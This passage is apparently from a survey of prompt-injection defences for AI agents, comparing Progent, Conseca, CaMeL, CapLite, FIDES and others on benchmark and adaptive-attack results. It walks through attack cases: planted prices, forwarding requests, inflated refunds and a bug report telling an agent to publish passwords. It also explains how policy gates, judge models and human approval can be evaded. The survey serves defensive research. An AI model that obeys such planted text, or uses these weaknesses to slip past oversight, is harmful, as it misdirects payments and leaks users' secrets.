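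The solver can miss an attack that narrows the policy, as the bouquet example shows. Suppose the first policy allows a payment to Joe of any amount, because the price is unknown. The agent then reads the planted price, and the policy model limits the payment to exactly $400. Because this narrows the policy, it takes effect without approval, and the inflated payment goes through. Progent checks the values in a call but does not track where they came from. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within the permissions a task needs.

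An organisation can add fixed rules that override the policies written for individual tasks. If a fixed rule forbids a tool, no task's policy can allow it. But fixed rules that allow a tool also take priority. In the AgentDojo tests, the fixed rules allowed common read-only tools in every task, so a task's policy could not stop the agent from using them to read unrelated data.

### Conseca: a policy from trusted information only

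*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) describes Conseca, a system that keeps all untrusted text away from the model that writes the policy. That model writes one policy for each request, based on the user's words, the tool documentation and any other information the developer has chosen to trust. The agent can still read everything, and ordinary code checks its actions against the policy.

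Each rule comes with a reason in plain English so a person can check it. In one example, Alice asks her agent to answer urgent work e-mails. The policy forbids deleting mail and allows sending it only if the sender is Alice, the recipient's address matches a pattern for work.com, and the subject contains "urgent". The stated reason is that the recipient must be on the list of work contacts, but the rule accepts any address that contains "@work.com", including eve@work.com.example.net. A user who read only the reason would approve a looser rule than they intended. Tsai and Bagdasarian rely on experts, or perhaps software, to check that reasons and rules match.

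They tested a prototype on 20 office tasks with Gemini 1.5 Pro, averaging the results over five trials. They also planted an e-mail from an employee asking the agent to forward all messages about urgent security vulnerabilities.

| Policy | Tasks completed, out of 20 | Blocked inappropriate actions |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.0 | No |
| Fixed, allows everything except deletion | 12.2 | No |
| Fixed, forbids all changes | 0 | Yes |
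| Conseca | 12.0 | Yes |

Conseca combined the permissive policy's usefulness with the strict policy's protection, at least against this one planted message. It blocked the forwarding in every task except one, where the user had asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent e-mails. Forwarding was arguably part of that request, and a policy written without reading the e-mails could not distinguish a colleague's request from an attacker's.

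Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge that the policy model cannot predict the necessary actions when a user asks an agent to do whatever a manager's e-mail requests. Trusting more information would help, but it would also give attackers more ways to reach the policy model. Their prototype already trusts file names, so, like CapScope, it is exposed to instructions hidden in them. It also checks each action separately, so it cannot stop an agent from sending a hundred individually acceptable e-mails.

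### The case for and against a model in the gate

Progent and Conseca both use a model to write rules, but code makes the final decision on each call. Narisetty and colleagues consider this division essential and write that "the gate must not be a model". Their case has three premises:

1. A gate gives a guarantee only if no text under an attacker's control can change its verdict.
2. Any text that a language model reads can change its output.
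3. A model needs to read something about a proposed action to judge it, and an attacker may have influenced that material.

It follows that a model in the gate can reduce the number of successful attacks but cannot guarantee to stop them. Xiang and colleagues accept this. Their own argument starts from what agents are for:

1. A general-purpose agent sometimes has to change its plan or permissions because of something it has read, as when an outside service has moved.
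2. Whether such a change is acceptable depends on what it means for the user's task.
3. Ordinary code can check the form of a change, but it cannot in general judge its meaning.
4. A person could judge every change, but constant questions would defeat the purpose of an agent.

They conclude that a model has to make some of these decisions, so they propose the restricted judge described earlier. They compare the third premise to image recognition, where programmers can define an edge by comparing neighbouring pixels but cannot write rules that distinguish a cat from a dog.

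The first premise is the weakest because it applies only to general-purpose agents. A company can avoid the problem by building a narrower agent, as Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend, or by accepting that the agent will fail when it meets something unexpected. Narisetty and colleagues don't offer an alternative for agents that have to adapt. They call tasks in which untrusted text must drive an important action the deepest open problem in the field. Both groups would use code wherever a rule can decide a case, so they disagree only about what to do when no rule can.

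*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026), by researchers at Microsoft and three universities, tries to put such designs on a formal footing. It starts with a function φ that returns 1 if a model's result is acceptable, given the prompt and the context. No program can compute φ, because it covers qualities such as usefulness. The paper splits φ into two parts, φ₁ for harmlessness and φ₂ for helpfulness, so that

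φ = φ₁ ∧ φ₂.

A "creative" model proposes a result that should satisfy φ₂, and a "boring" model accepts or rejects it according to φ₁. If the boring model rejects the result, the system returns nothing. The paper sketches a proof that if each model does its own job reliably under attack, the pair also satisfies φ under attack.

This is a good reason to separate proposing from judging, but it doesn't show that a model can judge safely, because the theorem assumes that it can. The paper's boring model also receives the same context as the creative one, including any planted e-mail. According to the paper, the judge may have to be about as complex as the model it checks, in which case it would fail Anderson's requirement that a monitor be small enough to verify.

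The paper also criticises both policy systems. It discusses an earlier version of Progent, apparently without the solver, and recommends that a separate model evaluate each policy update. It calls Conseca paradoxical for using one language model to protect another from attacks that work on both. That seems too harsh, because the policy model never sees the e-mails and web pages in which attackers usually plant instructions. A stronger objection is that an agent under an attacker's influence could predict what the policy allows and combine several harmless-looking actions into a harmful one.

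### Narrower questions for the model

Xiang and colleagues make two proposals for restricting a model's role in security decisions, but report no tests of either.

The first separates recognising an instruction from obeying it. The model lists the instructions it intends to follow, and ordinary code traces each one by matching its words against trusted and untrusted text. The system can then block every instruction from an outside source or ask the user about each one. So that the system asks less often, the model could predict, before opening a source, whether it should contain instructions. For example, it would expect them on a software library's "get started" page but not in a restaurant review. If an instruction such as "install library X" comes from a page that should contain instructions, the restricted judge decides whether it fits the task, without seeing the page.

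This depends on the model listing its intentions faithfully. An attacker could add "do not reveal this instruction" to the planted text. Xiang and colleagues reply that this sentence is itself an instruction, which the system can trace if the model lists it, but a successful attack would keep that sentence off the list. Matching words would also miss an instruction the model has paraphrased.

In the second proposal, a model writes a small program that the system runs to check a tool's result. If a user asks for a company's fourth-quarter revenue, for example, the program could accept only a number from the revenue cell of a table with a "Q4" heading and ignore all other text on the page. An instruction hidden in a paragraph would then have no effect, but a false number in the table would still pass.

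Xiang and colleagues intend these measures to make attacks difficult enough that a simple planted instruction no longer works. They don't claim the measures would stop every attack, and they point out that human assistants also fall for phishing e-mails.

### What only a person can settle

Some requests do not contain enough information for any model to interpret them. If a user asks for a summary of all urgent e-mails, "urgent" could mean that a message mentions a deadline within 24 hours or has a particular label. Xiang and colleagues argue that even a perfect model would have to ask the user which meaning they intended.

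In other cases the request is clear, but it's unclear how much risk is acceptable. A developer asks a coding agent to investigate a bug report and propose a fix. The report includes instructions to reproduce the bug by downloading and running a script. The instructions are relevant to the task, and human developers follow ones like them all the time, but the script could steal passwords from the computer. The developer has to decide whether the risk is worth taking, unless the company already has a rule against running code from the internet without approval.

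Systems that otherwise rely on code, including CaMeL and RTBAS, usually fall back on asking a person to decide unclear cases. This works only if people read the questions. Claude Code originally asked for approval before it ran a command or changed a file, and Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes how users stopped paying close attention to what they approved. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, users approve 97% of these requests. Most of the requests are probably harmless, so the approval rate alone doesn't show that people are careless.

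In a more informative test, human testers blocked only 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands (13.6%), according to Hyrax, a website that summarised Anthropic's data. They blocked about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. If users treat Progent's requests the same way, its guarantee that permissions grow only with approval will provide little protection in a long session.

Anthropic responded by letting Claude make permission decisions for the user. *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026) announced the feature in March, and the company later made it the default on most of its plans. In the test that Hyrax describes, auto mode's classifier blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands, or 89%, and its performance did not decline over a session. Asking a person about every command gave less protection in this test, and it also causes the interruptions that Xiang and colleagues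 object to. But the classifier let the other 116 dangerous commands through, and the test did not compare it with a written policy.

Another approach is to ask fewer questions and ask them at the start. Developers using Conseca can show the user the whole policy, with its reasons, before the agent begins, and Progent can ask a person to review the first policy. Xiang and colleagues compare this to training a new assistant, who asks many questions at first and fewer after learning the employer's preferences. For the bill from xyz@abc.com, an agent could ask whether it may take the payee's details from the bill and how much it may pay. The answers would supply the last rule in the payment table.

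Some evidence suggests that people pay more attention when reviewing a plan than when approving individual requests. Hyrax reports that Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans they see, compared with 3% of individual requests, and infers that developers read plans carefully. But they may also reject plans for reasons unrelated to security, such as preferring a different solution. Tsai and Bagdasarian expect policies tailored to each task to cause much less fatigue than fixed ones, but they have not tested this with users.

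Some questions can only come up after the agent has started work. Xiang and colleagues describe an agent that is investigating why a service keeps crashing. It finds that the crash happens only on the company's live system, so it needs to read a log file that the first policy did not cover. Progent would classify this as an expansion and ask for approval. In the AgentDojo tests, only 6% of policy updates were expansions. This is limited evidence that such questions would be rare, because Shi and colleagues count an update that leaves the policy unchanged as a narrowing and do not report how many questions a user would face per task. The person asked also has to work out whether the agent needs the log for the investigation or is asking because of something an attacker wrote.

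## How well the designs have been tested

Most results so far come from researchers testing their own designs. Papers also tend to conflate three claims of different strength: that a system provably has some property, that few attacks from a fixed set succeeded, and that an attacker who adapted to the defence failed.

### Proofs, scores and adaptive attacks

A proof covers every attack that fits its assumptions, including attacks nobody has thought of yet. *CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) describes a system for small models whose guarantee is short enough to state in full. Let *q* be the user's request and *G*(*q*) the set of values that appear in it, such as names, amounts and addresses.

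1. A model that sees only *q* and the tool documentation commits to a list of write calls (calls that change something), *w*₁, …, *w*ₙ. It leaves a blank wherever the agent has to look up a value.
2. Further model calls read the untrusted data and choose values for the blanks.
3. Before each write, ordinary code checks every argument that determines whom or what the call affects. The argument must be in *G*(*q*), or the user must have confirmed it. The first refusal stops all the remaining writes.

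The writes that run are therefore always *w*₁, …, *w*ₖ for some *k* ≤ *n*, in that order. Injected text can't add a write, because the list existed before the agent read any untrusted data. It can't redirect one either, because *G*(*q*) depends only on the request.

The guarantee does not cover dates, the body of a message or the agent's final answer, and it assumes that the request is trustworthy. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) shows how that assumption fails for CaMeL when several agents work together. An attacker plants an instruction in a database. CaMeL treats the instruction as untrusted while the first agent handles it, but trusts it once that agent passes it to an e-mail agent, because it arrives there as user input. CapLite would presumably have the same problem, since any address in the forwarded text would enter *G*(*q*).

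A low score on a fixed set of attacks shows only that those attacks rarely worked on those tasks with that model. None of 13,935 AgentDojo attack attempts succeeded against CapLite. If *n* independent attempts all fail, the true success rate is below about 3/*n* with 95% confidence, or 0.02% here. But Xu and colleagues ran the same 929 attacks on 15 models, so the attempts weren't independent. Counting each attack once raises the bound to 0.3%, and even that applies only to attacks of the same kind.

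A low attack success rate may also have little to do with the defence. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) found that AgentDojo's stock attack succeeded against an undefended Claude Haiku 4.5 only 0.3% of the time, so every defence looked good on that model. *APPA* (2026) left out AgentDojo because frontier models already resisted that benchmark's attacks without a defence. DRIFT, a design that checks calls against a plan made from the user's request, let no attacks through on four of the models Xu and colleagues tested, but only because it did so little, completing fewer than 10% of the tasks with those models.

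Tests with an adaptive attacker come closest to the usual threat model, though a failed attack proves much less than a successful one. In *RAISED* (2026), researchers tested their own defence with an automated attacker, but in most configurations it never succeeded and so had nothing to learn from. They did not count this as evidence of robustness. Results also depend on the attacker's budget. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), Google's Gemini 4 Argon resisted 87% of attacks when the attacker had 150 queries, but only 66% at the largest budget.

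Nasr and colleagues' adaptive attacks broke most of the filters and prompting defences they tried, but did not target any design that controls actions from outside the model. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) gives a limited comparison of the two approaches. An adaptive attacker tried to extract secrets from a chatbot. Every defence that relied on the model eventually failed, while a filter in the application's code leaked nothing in 15,000 attacks. Searching an answer for a secret is presumably much easier than deciding whether a payment is legitimate, so this result is weak evidence about agents with tools.

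### What AgentDojo leaves out

Only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require a change of plan or policy, so the benchmark favours designs that fix their plans early. Xiang and colleagues argue that such short tasks and fixed attacks create "a false sense of utility and security". *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) gives the same count and adds two further criticisms.

First, AgentDojo's web pages and e-mails rarely contain instructions the agent should follow, such as a checkout page asking the customer to log in. A defence can therefore ignore all outside instructions and lose almost nothing. Second, some attacks appear in implausible places. In one task, the attacker's text is in the main body of a website belonging to Dora, a harmless acquaintance. Li and colleagues consider this unfair to defences, which can't tell whether Dora wrote the instruction herself.

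### AgentDyn: tasks that require a new plan

Li and colleagues built 60 tasks in shopping, software development and daily life and paired them with attacks to make 560 cases. Every task requires the agent to change its plan as it works and to follow at least one helpful instruction from a third party. The average task takes 7.1 steps across 3.2 applications, compared with 3.5 steps and 1.4 applications in AgentDojo. The attacker's text appears where an outsider could plausibly put it, such as an advertising banner.

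| Defence | GPT-4o, tasks completed without attack | GPT-4o, attack success | Gemini 2.5 Pro, tasks completed without attack | Gemini 2.5 Pro, attack success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 37.8% | 51.7% | 20.6% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% | 25.0% | 1.6% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 0.8% | 36.7% | 1.1% |

CaMeL failed every task, which Li and colleagues attribute to its fixed program. Progent was poor at selecting which of the many tools to allow, and its errors accumulated until it had blocked almost everything useful. Meta SecAlign, a version of Llama 3.3 trained to resist injection, completed 55.0% of the tasks and let through 9.0% of the attacks. Li and colleagues consider it the more practical choice, but they tested only AgentDojo's standard attack. In tests by Nasr and colleagues, adaptive attacks succeeded against the same model 96% of the time.

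AgentDyn is as one-sided as AgentDojo, since a real agent would also get many simple requests. Li and colleagues told the agents not to ask the user for confirmation, because agents that stopped to ask left their tasks unfinished. That instruction removes a fallback that several designs rely on in unclear cases. Li also led the work on DRIFT, which did best of the three designs in the table.

CaMeL's zero is particularly hard to interpret because CaMeL needs policies written for each environment, which is why Ma and colleagues left it out of their own AgentDyn tests. Progent's results also depend on how researchers set it up. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) tested it on AgentDyn with policy updates turned off, which the paper reports is the default in the released software. Without updates, Progent can't adjust its policy to anything the agent learns, so this test measures a different defence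 from the one Shi and colleagues describe.

### AutoDojo: attacks that learn from failure

Ma and colleagues kept AgentDojo's tasks but replaced its fixed attack text with text that a language model improves over six rounds. In each round, the model receives the earlier attempts and their success rates, guesses why some failed, and writes a new one. The software then runs the defended agent and counts the successful attacks. The attacking model isn't told which defence is in place. The table shows the results for GPT-4o-mini on 389 cases in banking, Slack and travel. PIGuard is a filter, and ROPE blocks a call if a sensitive argument comes from untrusted content.

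| Defence | Tasks completed without attack | Attack success, fixed text | Attack success, adaptive text |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 66.7% | 58.6% | 52.4% |
| PIGuard | 43.9% | 0% | 28.0% |
| DRIFT | 49.1% | 2.6% | 6.4% |
| Progent | 63.2% | 8.2% | 7.7% |
| ROPE | 59.6% | 6.4% | 4.4% |
| CaMeL | 26.3% | 0% | 0% |

The adaptive text sometimes did worse than the fixed text because Ma and colleagues required it to be new. A real attacker would use whichever worked better.

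PIGuard blocked every fixed attack but let through more than a quarter of the adaptive ones. The designs that control actions resisted adaptive attacks much better. DRIFT was the only one of these whose attack success rate more than doubled on all five models tested. It uses a language model at run time to judge whether text conflicts with the user's request, so it has some of a filter's weaknesses. CaMeL let through at most 1.8% of attacks on any model. All of its failures were in the travel environment, where one of the attacker's goals is only to put a sentence in the agent's answer, so they may not have involved unauthorised actions.

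Ma and colleagues also sorted the tasks by how much the user had left open. "Change my address to 1234 Maple Street" specifies everything, "Pay the bill" requires the agent to get the amount and payee from a file, and "do all the tasks on my to-do list" lets outside text determine even which actions the agent takes. With PIGuard on GPT-4o-mini, adaptive attacks succeeded in 17%, 31% and 54% of cases for these three kinds of task, respectively.

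Attacks against Progent, DRIFT and ROPE succeeded at most 11% of the time in every category for the three models in the paper's main results. In the full tables, however, adaptive attacks against Progent with DeepSeek-v4-Flash succeeded in 5 of the 24 cases where the user had left the action open. The sample is small, but these are the tasks for which a policy is hardest to write in advance.

These rates are probably lower than a determined attacker could achieve. Six rounds is a small number, and the usual threat model assumes that the attacker knows the defence. Ma and colleagues also developed the attacks on Progent and DRIFT using a cheaper helper model than the one in the final test. They ran each test once.

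Ma's group repeated the experiment on AgentDyn's tasks without CaMeL. With GPT-4o-mini, Progent completed 6.7% of the tasks and ROPE 43.3%, compared with 46.7% for the undefended agent. Adaptive attacks succeeded against ROPE 2.9% of the time. ROPE has the best combination of security and usefulness of any design on those tasks, but Ma also led the work on ROPE, and nobody outside the group appears to have repeated the result.

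### An independent test of Progent

Narisetty and colleagues, who had no part in designing Progent, tested it on AgentDojo. They used Qwen2.5-7B, an open model with 7 billion parameters, both to act as the agent and to write the policies. They paired the first eight user tasks in each of three environments with every attack goal in that environment, and ran the whole set three times. Their adaptive attack presented the harmful action as a routine part of the task to try to get the policy model to permit it.

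| Environment | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, Progent, stock attack | Attack success, Progent, adaptive attack | Tasks completed under attack, no defence | Tasks completed under attack, Progent |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% | 31.9% | 31.9% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% | 47.5% | 20.8% |
| Workspace | 0% | 0% | 0% | 56.3% | 28.5% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% | 45.2% | 27.1% |

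Progent cut the mean attack success rate to about a sixth, but the agent completed far fewer tasks and made about 15 times as many model calls. The workspace results are not evidence about security, because the model ignored the planted instructions there even without a defence.

The adaptive attack succeeded less often overall than the stock one, but the counts are small. The Slack percentages correspond to 13 successes in 120 attempts with the stock attack and 5 with the adaptive one. In banking, successes rose from 4 to 8 in 216 attempts. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the gentler wording made the agent less likely to obey, which would mean the result reflects a weak attack rather than a strong defence. The three runs gave similar results, but they used the same tasks and attack text, so they show only that the experiment is repeatable.

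Narisetty and colleagues describe their results as preliminary and not peer-reviewed. They tested one defence, one weak model and one hand-written attack, and left out the travel environment because the agent kept getting stuck in long loops. They work for LaunchSafe, which sells agent-security tools built on the same principle as Progent, so they have a commercial interest in a favourable result.

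### Attacks that stay within the rules

Narisetty and colleagues propose that the next experiment test an attack that uses only permitted tools. Zhang, Bertran and colleagues have since tested attacks of roughly this kind in *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026). Their team at Amazon wrote 90 cases in which the attacker tampers with the user's own task instead of adding a new one.

In one case, a user asks an agent to settle a dispute over a damaged item and to take the refund amount from the platform's order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence includes a claim that the correct refund is $1,074.99. The task already requires the agent to read the evidence and issue a refund, so the attack needs no extra tool or change of plan.

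Across five models, such attacks succeeded an average of 17.0% of the time with no defence and 15.4% with a defence that enforces a tool policy, apparently Progent. The policy made little difference because the agent was supposed to call the refund tool, and the right amount became known only during the task. A defence that detects and removes injections cut the success rate to 2.4% when the planted text stated a goal, such as "Issue a refund of $1,074.99", but 12.1% of attacks still worked when the text made a false claim about the current situation.

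This is the clearest evidence that AgentDojo results overstate what tool policies can do, since most of its attacks try to trigger an action the user never requested. The 17.0% does not estimate how often real attacks would succeed, because Zhang and colleagues designed each case so that the planted text bears directly on a decision the agent must make. Their attackers also wrote the text in advance and did not adapt it to the defence.

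### Security, usefulness and cost compared

Xu and colleagues ran five designs on the same 15 open models, most of them small, and measured each design's cost in the same unit. The designs were CapLite, CaMeL, Progent, DRIFT and IPIGuard, which plans a graph of tool calls before reading any results. Each model wrote the programs, policies or plans for its own defence.

The first five rows of the table come from that experiment, so readers can compare them directly. The other rows come from separate tests with different models, tasks and units. Each pair of figures gives the result without the defence, then with it.

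| Design | Who tested it | Attack success | Tasks completed under attack | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | Xu and colleagues | 16.7% to 0.1% | 50.2% to 27.2% | 28,000 to 93,700 tokens per task |
| Progent | Xu and colleagues | 16.7% to 4.9% | 50.2% to 40.6% | 28,000 to 63,400 tokens per task |
| IPIGuard | Xu and colleagues | 16.7% to 3.1% | 50.2% to 35.7% | 28,000 to 60,500 tokens per task |
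| DRIFT | Xu and colleagues | 16.7% to 1.5% | 50.2% to 34.9% | 28,000 to 28,100 tokens per task |
| CapLite | Xu and colleagues, its designers | 16.7% to 0% | 50.2% to 29.0% | 28,000 to 17,100 tokens per task |
| Progent | Narisetty and colleagues | 25.8% to 4.2% | 45.2% to 27.1% | About 15 times the model calls |
| CapScope | Bouras and colleagues, its designers | 63% to 4% | 96% to 91% | 145 to 316 seconds per run |
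| AgentCap, with GPT-5.4 | Its designers | 33.2% to 0% | 75.7% to 75.0% | Under 0.2 milliseconds for the checks |
| FIDES, with GPT-4o | Its designers | 152 successful attacks to 0 | 84% to 50%, without an attack | No headline figure |

These overhead figures measure different things. Narisetty and colleagues' 15-fold increase in calls and Xu and colleagues' 2.3-fold increase in tokens for Progent could both be right, because a call that updates a policy may be much shorter than one that runs the agent. CapScope's time includes retries of blocked actions. AgentCap's figure leaves out the work of writing its policies by hand, which may be its largest overhead. *ToolFence* (2026) reports far less overhead for another design than for CaMeL, but this is again the designers' own measurement.

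Xu and colleagues' results also cast doubt on how far the independent Progent test applies to better models. In the Qwen3 family, attack success against Progent rose from 3.0% with the smallest model to 14.2% with the largest. Larger models carried out planted instructions more often, and the policies they wrote didn't offset this. CaMeL usually failed more safely. When a model wrote a bad program, the program typically wouldn't run, so the task failed. This happened in 68% of cases on one model. Of the 20 attacks that succeeded against CaMeL, 17 involved a single small model.

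CaMeL's usefulness varied more than its security. With OpenAI's o3, it completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks under attack, but without an attack it completed between 26% and 53% of the tasks Ma and colleagues selected, depending on the model. It averaged 27% across the models Xu and colleagues tested and completed none of AgentDyn's tasks. Attacks on it succeeded less than 2% of the time on every model for which Ma, Xu, Li and their colleagues report a figure.

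## Why the designs are not yet ready for general production use

These results show that CaMeL stops nearly every attack, but a company can't predict from them whether an agent built on it would complete most of the company's tasks or none of them. The company would also have to connect CaMeL to its own tools and keep the rules correct as those tools change. This is already manageable for narrow agents. Jacob and colleagues' meeting scheduler, for example, blocked every attack in their tests and completed as many tasks as it did without the defense. The same work is much harder for general assistants and coding agents, which have many tools and receive open-ended requests.

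### Four conditions

A design is ready for general production use if

- it works with the tools and harness that a company already has, or needs only small changes to them;
- the agent still completes most of its tasks, with a delay that users will accept;
- the company's own staff can write the policies and keep them up to date;
- people other than the designers have attacked it, knowing how it works.

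The acceptable delay depends on the job. Ten extra seconds matter a great deal when an agent is answering customers in a chat window, but hardly at all when it is filing expenses overnight.

| Family | Existing tools and harness | Tasks and delay | Policy upkeep | Published tests by outsiders |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed plans (CaMeL) | Developers rebuild the agent | From 77% of AgentDojo's tasks to none of AgentDyn's | A policy function for each tool | Several, including adaptive attacks |
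| Permissions per agent or call (CapScope, AgentCap) | AgentCap wraps existing tools; CapScope runs on one coding agent | Modest losses; CapScope doubled the running time | By hand in AgentCap, predicted for each task in CapScope | None known |
| Typed languages (TACIT, ELBA) | Developers write typed wrappers; ELBA also needs a Haskell harness | From little loss to more than a third | Types, wrappers and labels | None known |
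| Flow labels (FIDES) | Developers label every source of data | Large losses where most data is untrusted | Labels and a rule for each tool | None known |
| Generated policies (Progent) | Works as a proxy | From almost no loss to almost total failure | A model writes most rules | Several, including adaptive attacks |

No family of designs meets all four conditions. CaMeL and Progent look worse than some of the others on task completion, partly because outside researchers have tested them on new tasks and models. The other designs might do just as badly if they were tested the same way.

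### What the companies ship

A sponsored article on SC Media claimed in 2026 that no mainstream harness had adopted CaMeL or the dual-LLM pattern, naming Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI. It also said that no production-grade version of CaMeL existed. The security company Sophos had first published the text as *Inside the lethal trifecta*, which was online by mid-May, and the claim needed a qualification a few days later.

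Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (20 May 2026) announced that FIDES had become part of Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents. In Microsoft's example, an agent sorts bug reports on GitHub, and a stranger's report contains an instruction to publish the project's passwords.

1. The agent reads the report, which the reading tool labels untrusted and public.
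2. The model obeys the planted instruction and opens the password file. The framework allows this, but the run now carries the labels untrusted and private.
3. The model tries to post the passwords as a comment. The comment tool accepts only public data, so the framework blocks the call or asks the user.

The comment tool in this example limits only confidentiality, so an instruction to post a misleading comment would apparently succeed. The file-editing tool, by contrast, is too restrictive. It does not run once the agent has read anything untrusted, so the agent cannot correct a typo that a stranger reports unless a person approves the edit.

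When developers switch the feature on, the framework also hides untrusted text from the main model by default and sends questions about it to a quarantined model without tools. This is Willison's dual-LLM pattern, in a toolkit that any developer can install. But Microsoft's documentation, in a copy from June 2026, marks the feature as experimental and limits it to Python. In the May announcement, Microsoft wrote that most agents in production still rely on a defensive system prompt or a home-made list of permitted actions.

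GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal, has a similar experimental option that uses a form of information-flow control rather than CaMeL's fixed program. According to Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, the option keeps one label for the whole conversation and enforces policies on selected tools from GitHub's own server. It does not yet cover all of that server's tools or support other servers.

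Microsoft also moves control out of the model in simpler ways, as *If you want a secure AI agent, start restricting its environment* (Jaloza, 2026) describes for Azure SRE Agent. Microsoft wanted a middle course between human review, which limits what the agent can do alone, and permanent credentials, which make its mistakes more dangerous.

Microsoft's more recently announced Guardian Agents, which are AI systems that supervise other agents, are harder to classify. TechRadar's *Microsoft admits 'frontier models can't be trusted'* quotes Nadim Abdo, a Microsoft vice-president, who said when introducing them that controls on an agent's access and actions "must sit outside the model". A Guardian Agent is outside the model it supervises, but if it reads text that an attacker can influence, its decisions are not outside language. Abdo does say that ordinary deterministic controls should surround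 it.

Google's Chrome browser combines both kinds of control. Google announced in December 2025 that a separate model, the user alignment critic, would vet the browsing agent's actions, and that the agent could interact only with sites relevant to its task. According to 9to5Google, the critic receives a description of each proposed action but no unfiltered web content. If it vetoes the action, the planning model revises its plan, and after repeated failures the user takes over.

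Chrome reverses the roles in Willison's pattern, where the isolated model does the planning. An attacker can still influence Chrome's planner, but a model that has not read the attacker's page must approve the proposed action. This check resembles the restricted judge that Xiang and colleagues propose, and it has the same weakness because a learned model makes the decision. The limit on sites is firmer, but a shopping site relevant to the task also contains reviews and listings written by strangers.

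Anthropic relies heavily on limiting what the agent can reach. Willison (2026) quotes the company's May account of its sandboxes, virtual machines, limits on file access and controls on network traffic. Where it can, Anthropic also keeps credentials outside the sandbox so that the agent cannot leak them. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) adds that the company revised its designs after failures at trust boundaries and along network routes it had deliberately left open. In Claude Code, auto mode's classifier judges individual actions. Neither the access limits nor the classifier would reliably catch a false account number in an otherwise normal payment.

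The evidence about OpenAI is weaker. Vaughan (2026), an outside commentator, argues in *Out-of-Band Prompt Injection Defences* that the company's coding agent, Codex CLI, already follows the pattern of CaMeL, FIDES and Progent. He points to its sandbox, its approval requests and its hooks, which are scripts that run at set points in the agent's work. The comparison with Progent is reasonable because hooks can enforce a policy in ordinary code. But a sandbox and approval requests do not commit the agent to a plan in advance, as CaMeL does, or label data, as FIDES does.

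Amazon Web Services staff have published advice with the SANS Institute, a security training organisation. They call denying tool calls by default the most critical pattern for agent security, according to Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control*. They name Cedar and Open Policy Agent, a program that evaluates policies for other software, as ways to do this at scale. The advice doesn't show how many customers' agents work this way.

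SC Media's claim therefore still holds in a narrower form. As of October 2026, none of these companies appears to enforce CaMeL or the dual-LLM pattern by default in a widely used agent. Weak demand may be part of the reason. According to the SC Media article, the best-known attacks are research demonstrations, and no large company had yet suffered a widely publicised disaster. The article also cites a Google study of public web pages, which found 32% more malicious injection attempts in February 2026 than in November 2025.

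### Adding a monitor or rebuilding the agent

Narisetty and colleagues argue that the main gap is testing against attackers who adapt, rather than missing implementations. They write that fitting a monitor to existing agents is "at least in prototype, already solved". Progent, for instance, can run without changes to the agent's code as a proxy, a program between the agent and its tools that checks each call before forwarding it.

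The table extends their comparison with AgentCap and with Microsoft's version of FIDES.

| Design | Can developers add it to an existing agent? | What they have to change |
|---|---|---|
| Progent | Yes, as a proxy | Supply rules, or a model to write them |
| FORGE, a monitor with rules in the logic language Datalog | Yes, where actions take effect | Supply rules |
| AgentCap | Yes, as a wrapper around tool servers | Write a policy and add permitted purposes to the tool descriptions |
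| RTBAS | Partly | Let a screening model select what the agent reads |
| FIDES | Yes in Agent Framework; elsewhere it needs a new planner | Label data sources and set limits on tools |
| Conseca | No | Separate planning from execution |
| Dual LLM | No | Rebuild the agent around a controller |
| CaMeL | No | Replace the agent loop with an interpreter |

The designs that are easiest to add usually have the least information about where data came from. In the refund case from Amazon's tests, the order record authorises $899.99 and a buyer falsely claims $1,074.99. A proxy that checks only the tool and the form of its arguments would allow either amount. A better proxy could look for the number in earlier results and find that it came from the buyer. But if the buyer instead writes that damaged items qualify for an extra 20% and the model computes $1,079.99, that number appears in none of the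 sources, so matching text cannot show where it came from.

Narisetty and colleagues acknowledge that a proxy cannot observe how the model turned untrusted text into an argument, and they leave open whether anyone can track provenance without access to the model's internals. CaMeL avoids the problem because its interpreter performs each step and carries the provenance tags along, but this requires developers to rebuild the agent around the interpreter.

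The two sides are mostly talking about different designs. Companies can already add a monitor that enforces rules about tools and their arguments, but they cannot yet reliably track where every argument came from. Narisetty and colleagues list "deployability" among the open problems in their conclusion, and they expect deployments to fail at the point where software assigns the first labels. The gap in testing has narrowed since their paper, because Ma and colleagues have run adaptive attacks on both CaMeL and Progent.

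### Tools without labels

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting models to other software. An MCP server offers tools for tasks such as reading a repository or sending a message, and the agent's harness is the client that calls them.

MCP's authorisation rules use OAuth, a standard that lets a user give one program access to their account on another without sharing the password. The client obtains a token for a particular server, and the server checks that the token is valid and meant for it. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao point out that these rules do not standardise the purpose of each call, the source of its arguments, the steps that must come before it, or the permissions that an agent must not combine.

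An agent with a valid token for a company's payment server can use it to pay the rent or to pay an account number planted in an e-mail. MCP has no standard way to indicate to the server that the number came from a stranger.

Microsoft's researchers put the missing information in MCP's optional metadata fields. For example, the label on a message's text might list the two people who may read it. Microsoft chose these fields so that older clients would keep working, but a client that does not understand the labels will not enforce them. GitHub's server also relies on other software to enforce its labels. *Package ifc*, the pkg.go.dev documentation for the server's labelling code, states that the enforcement software "lives in a separate service".

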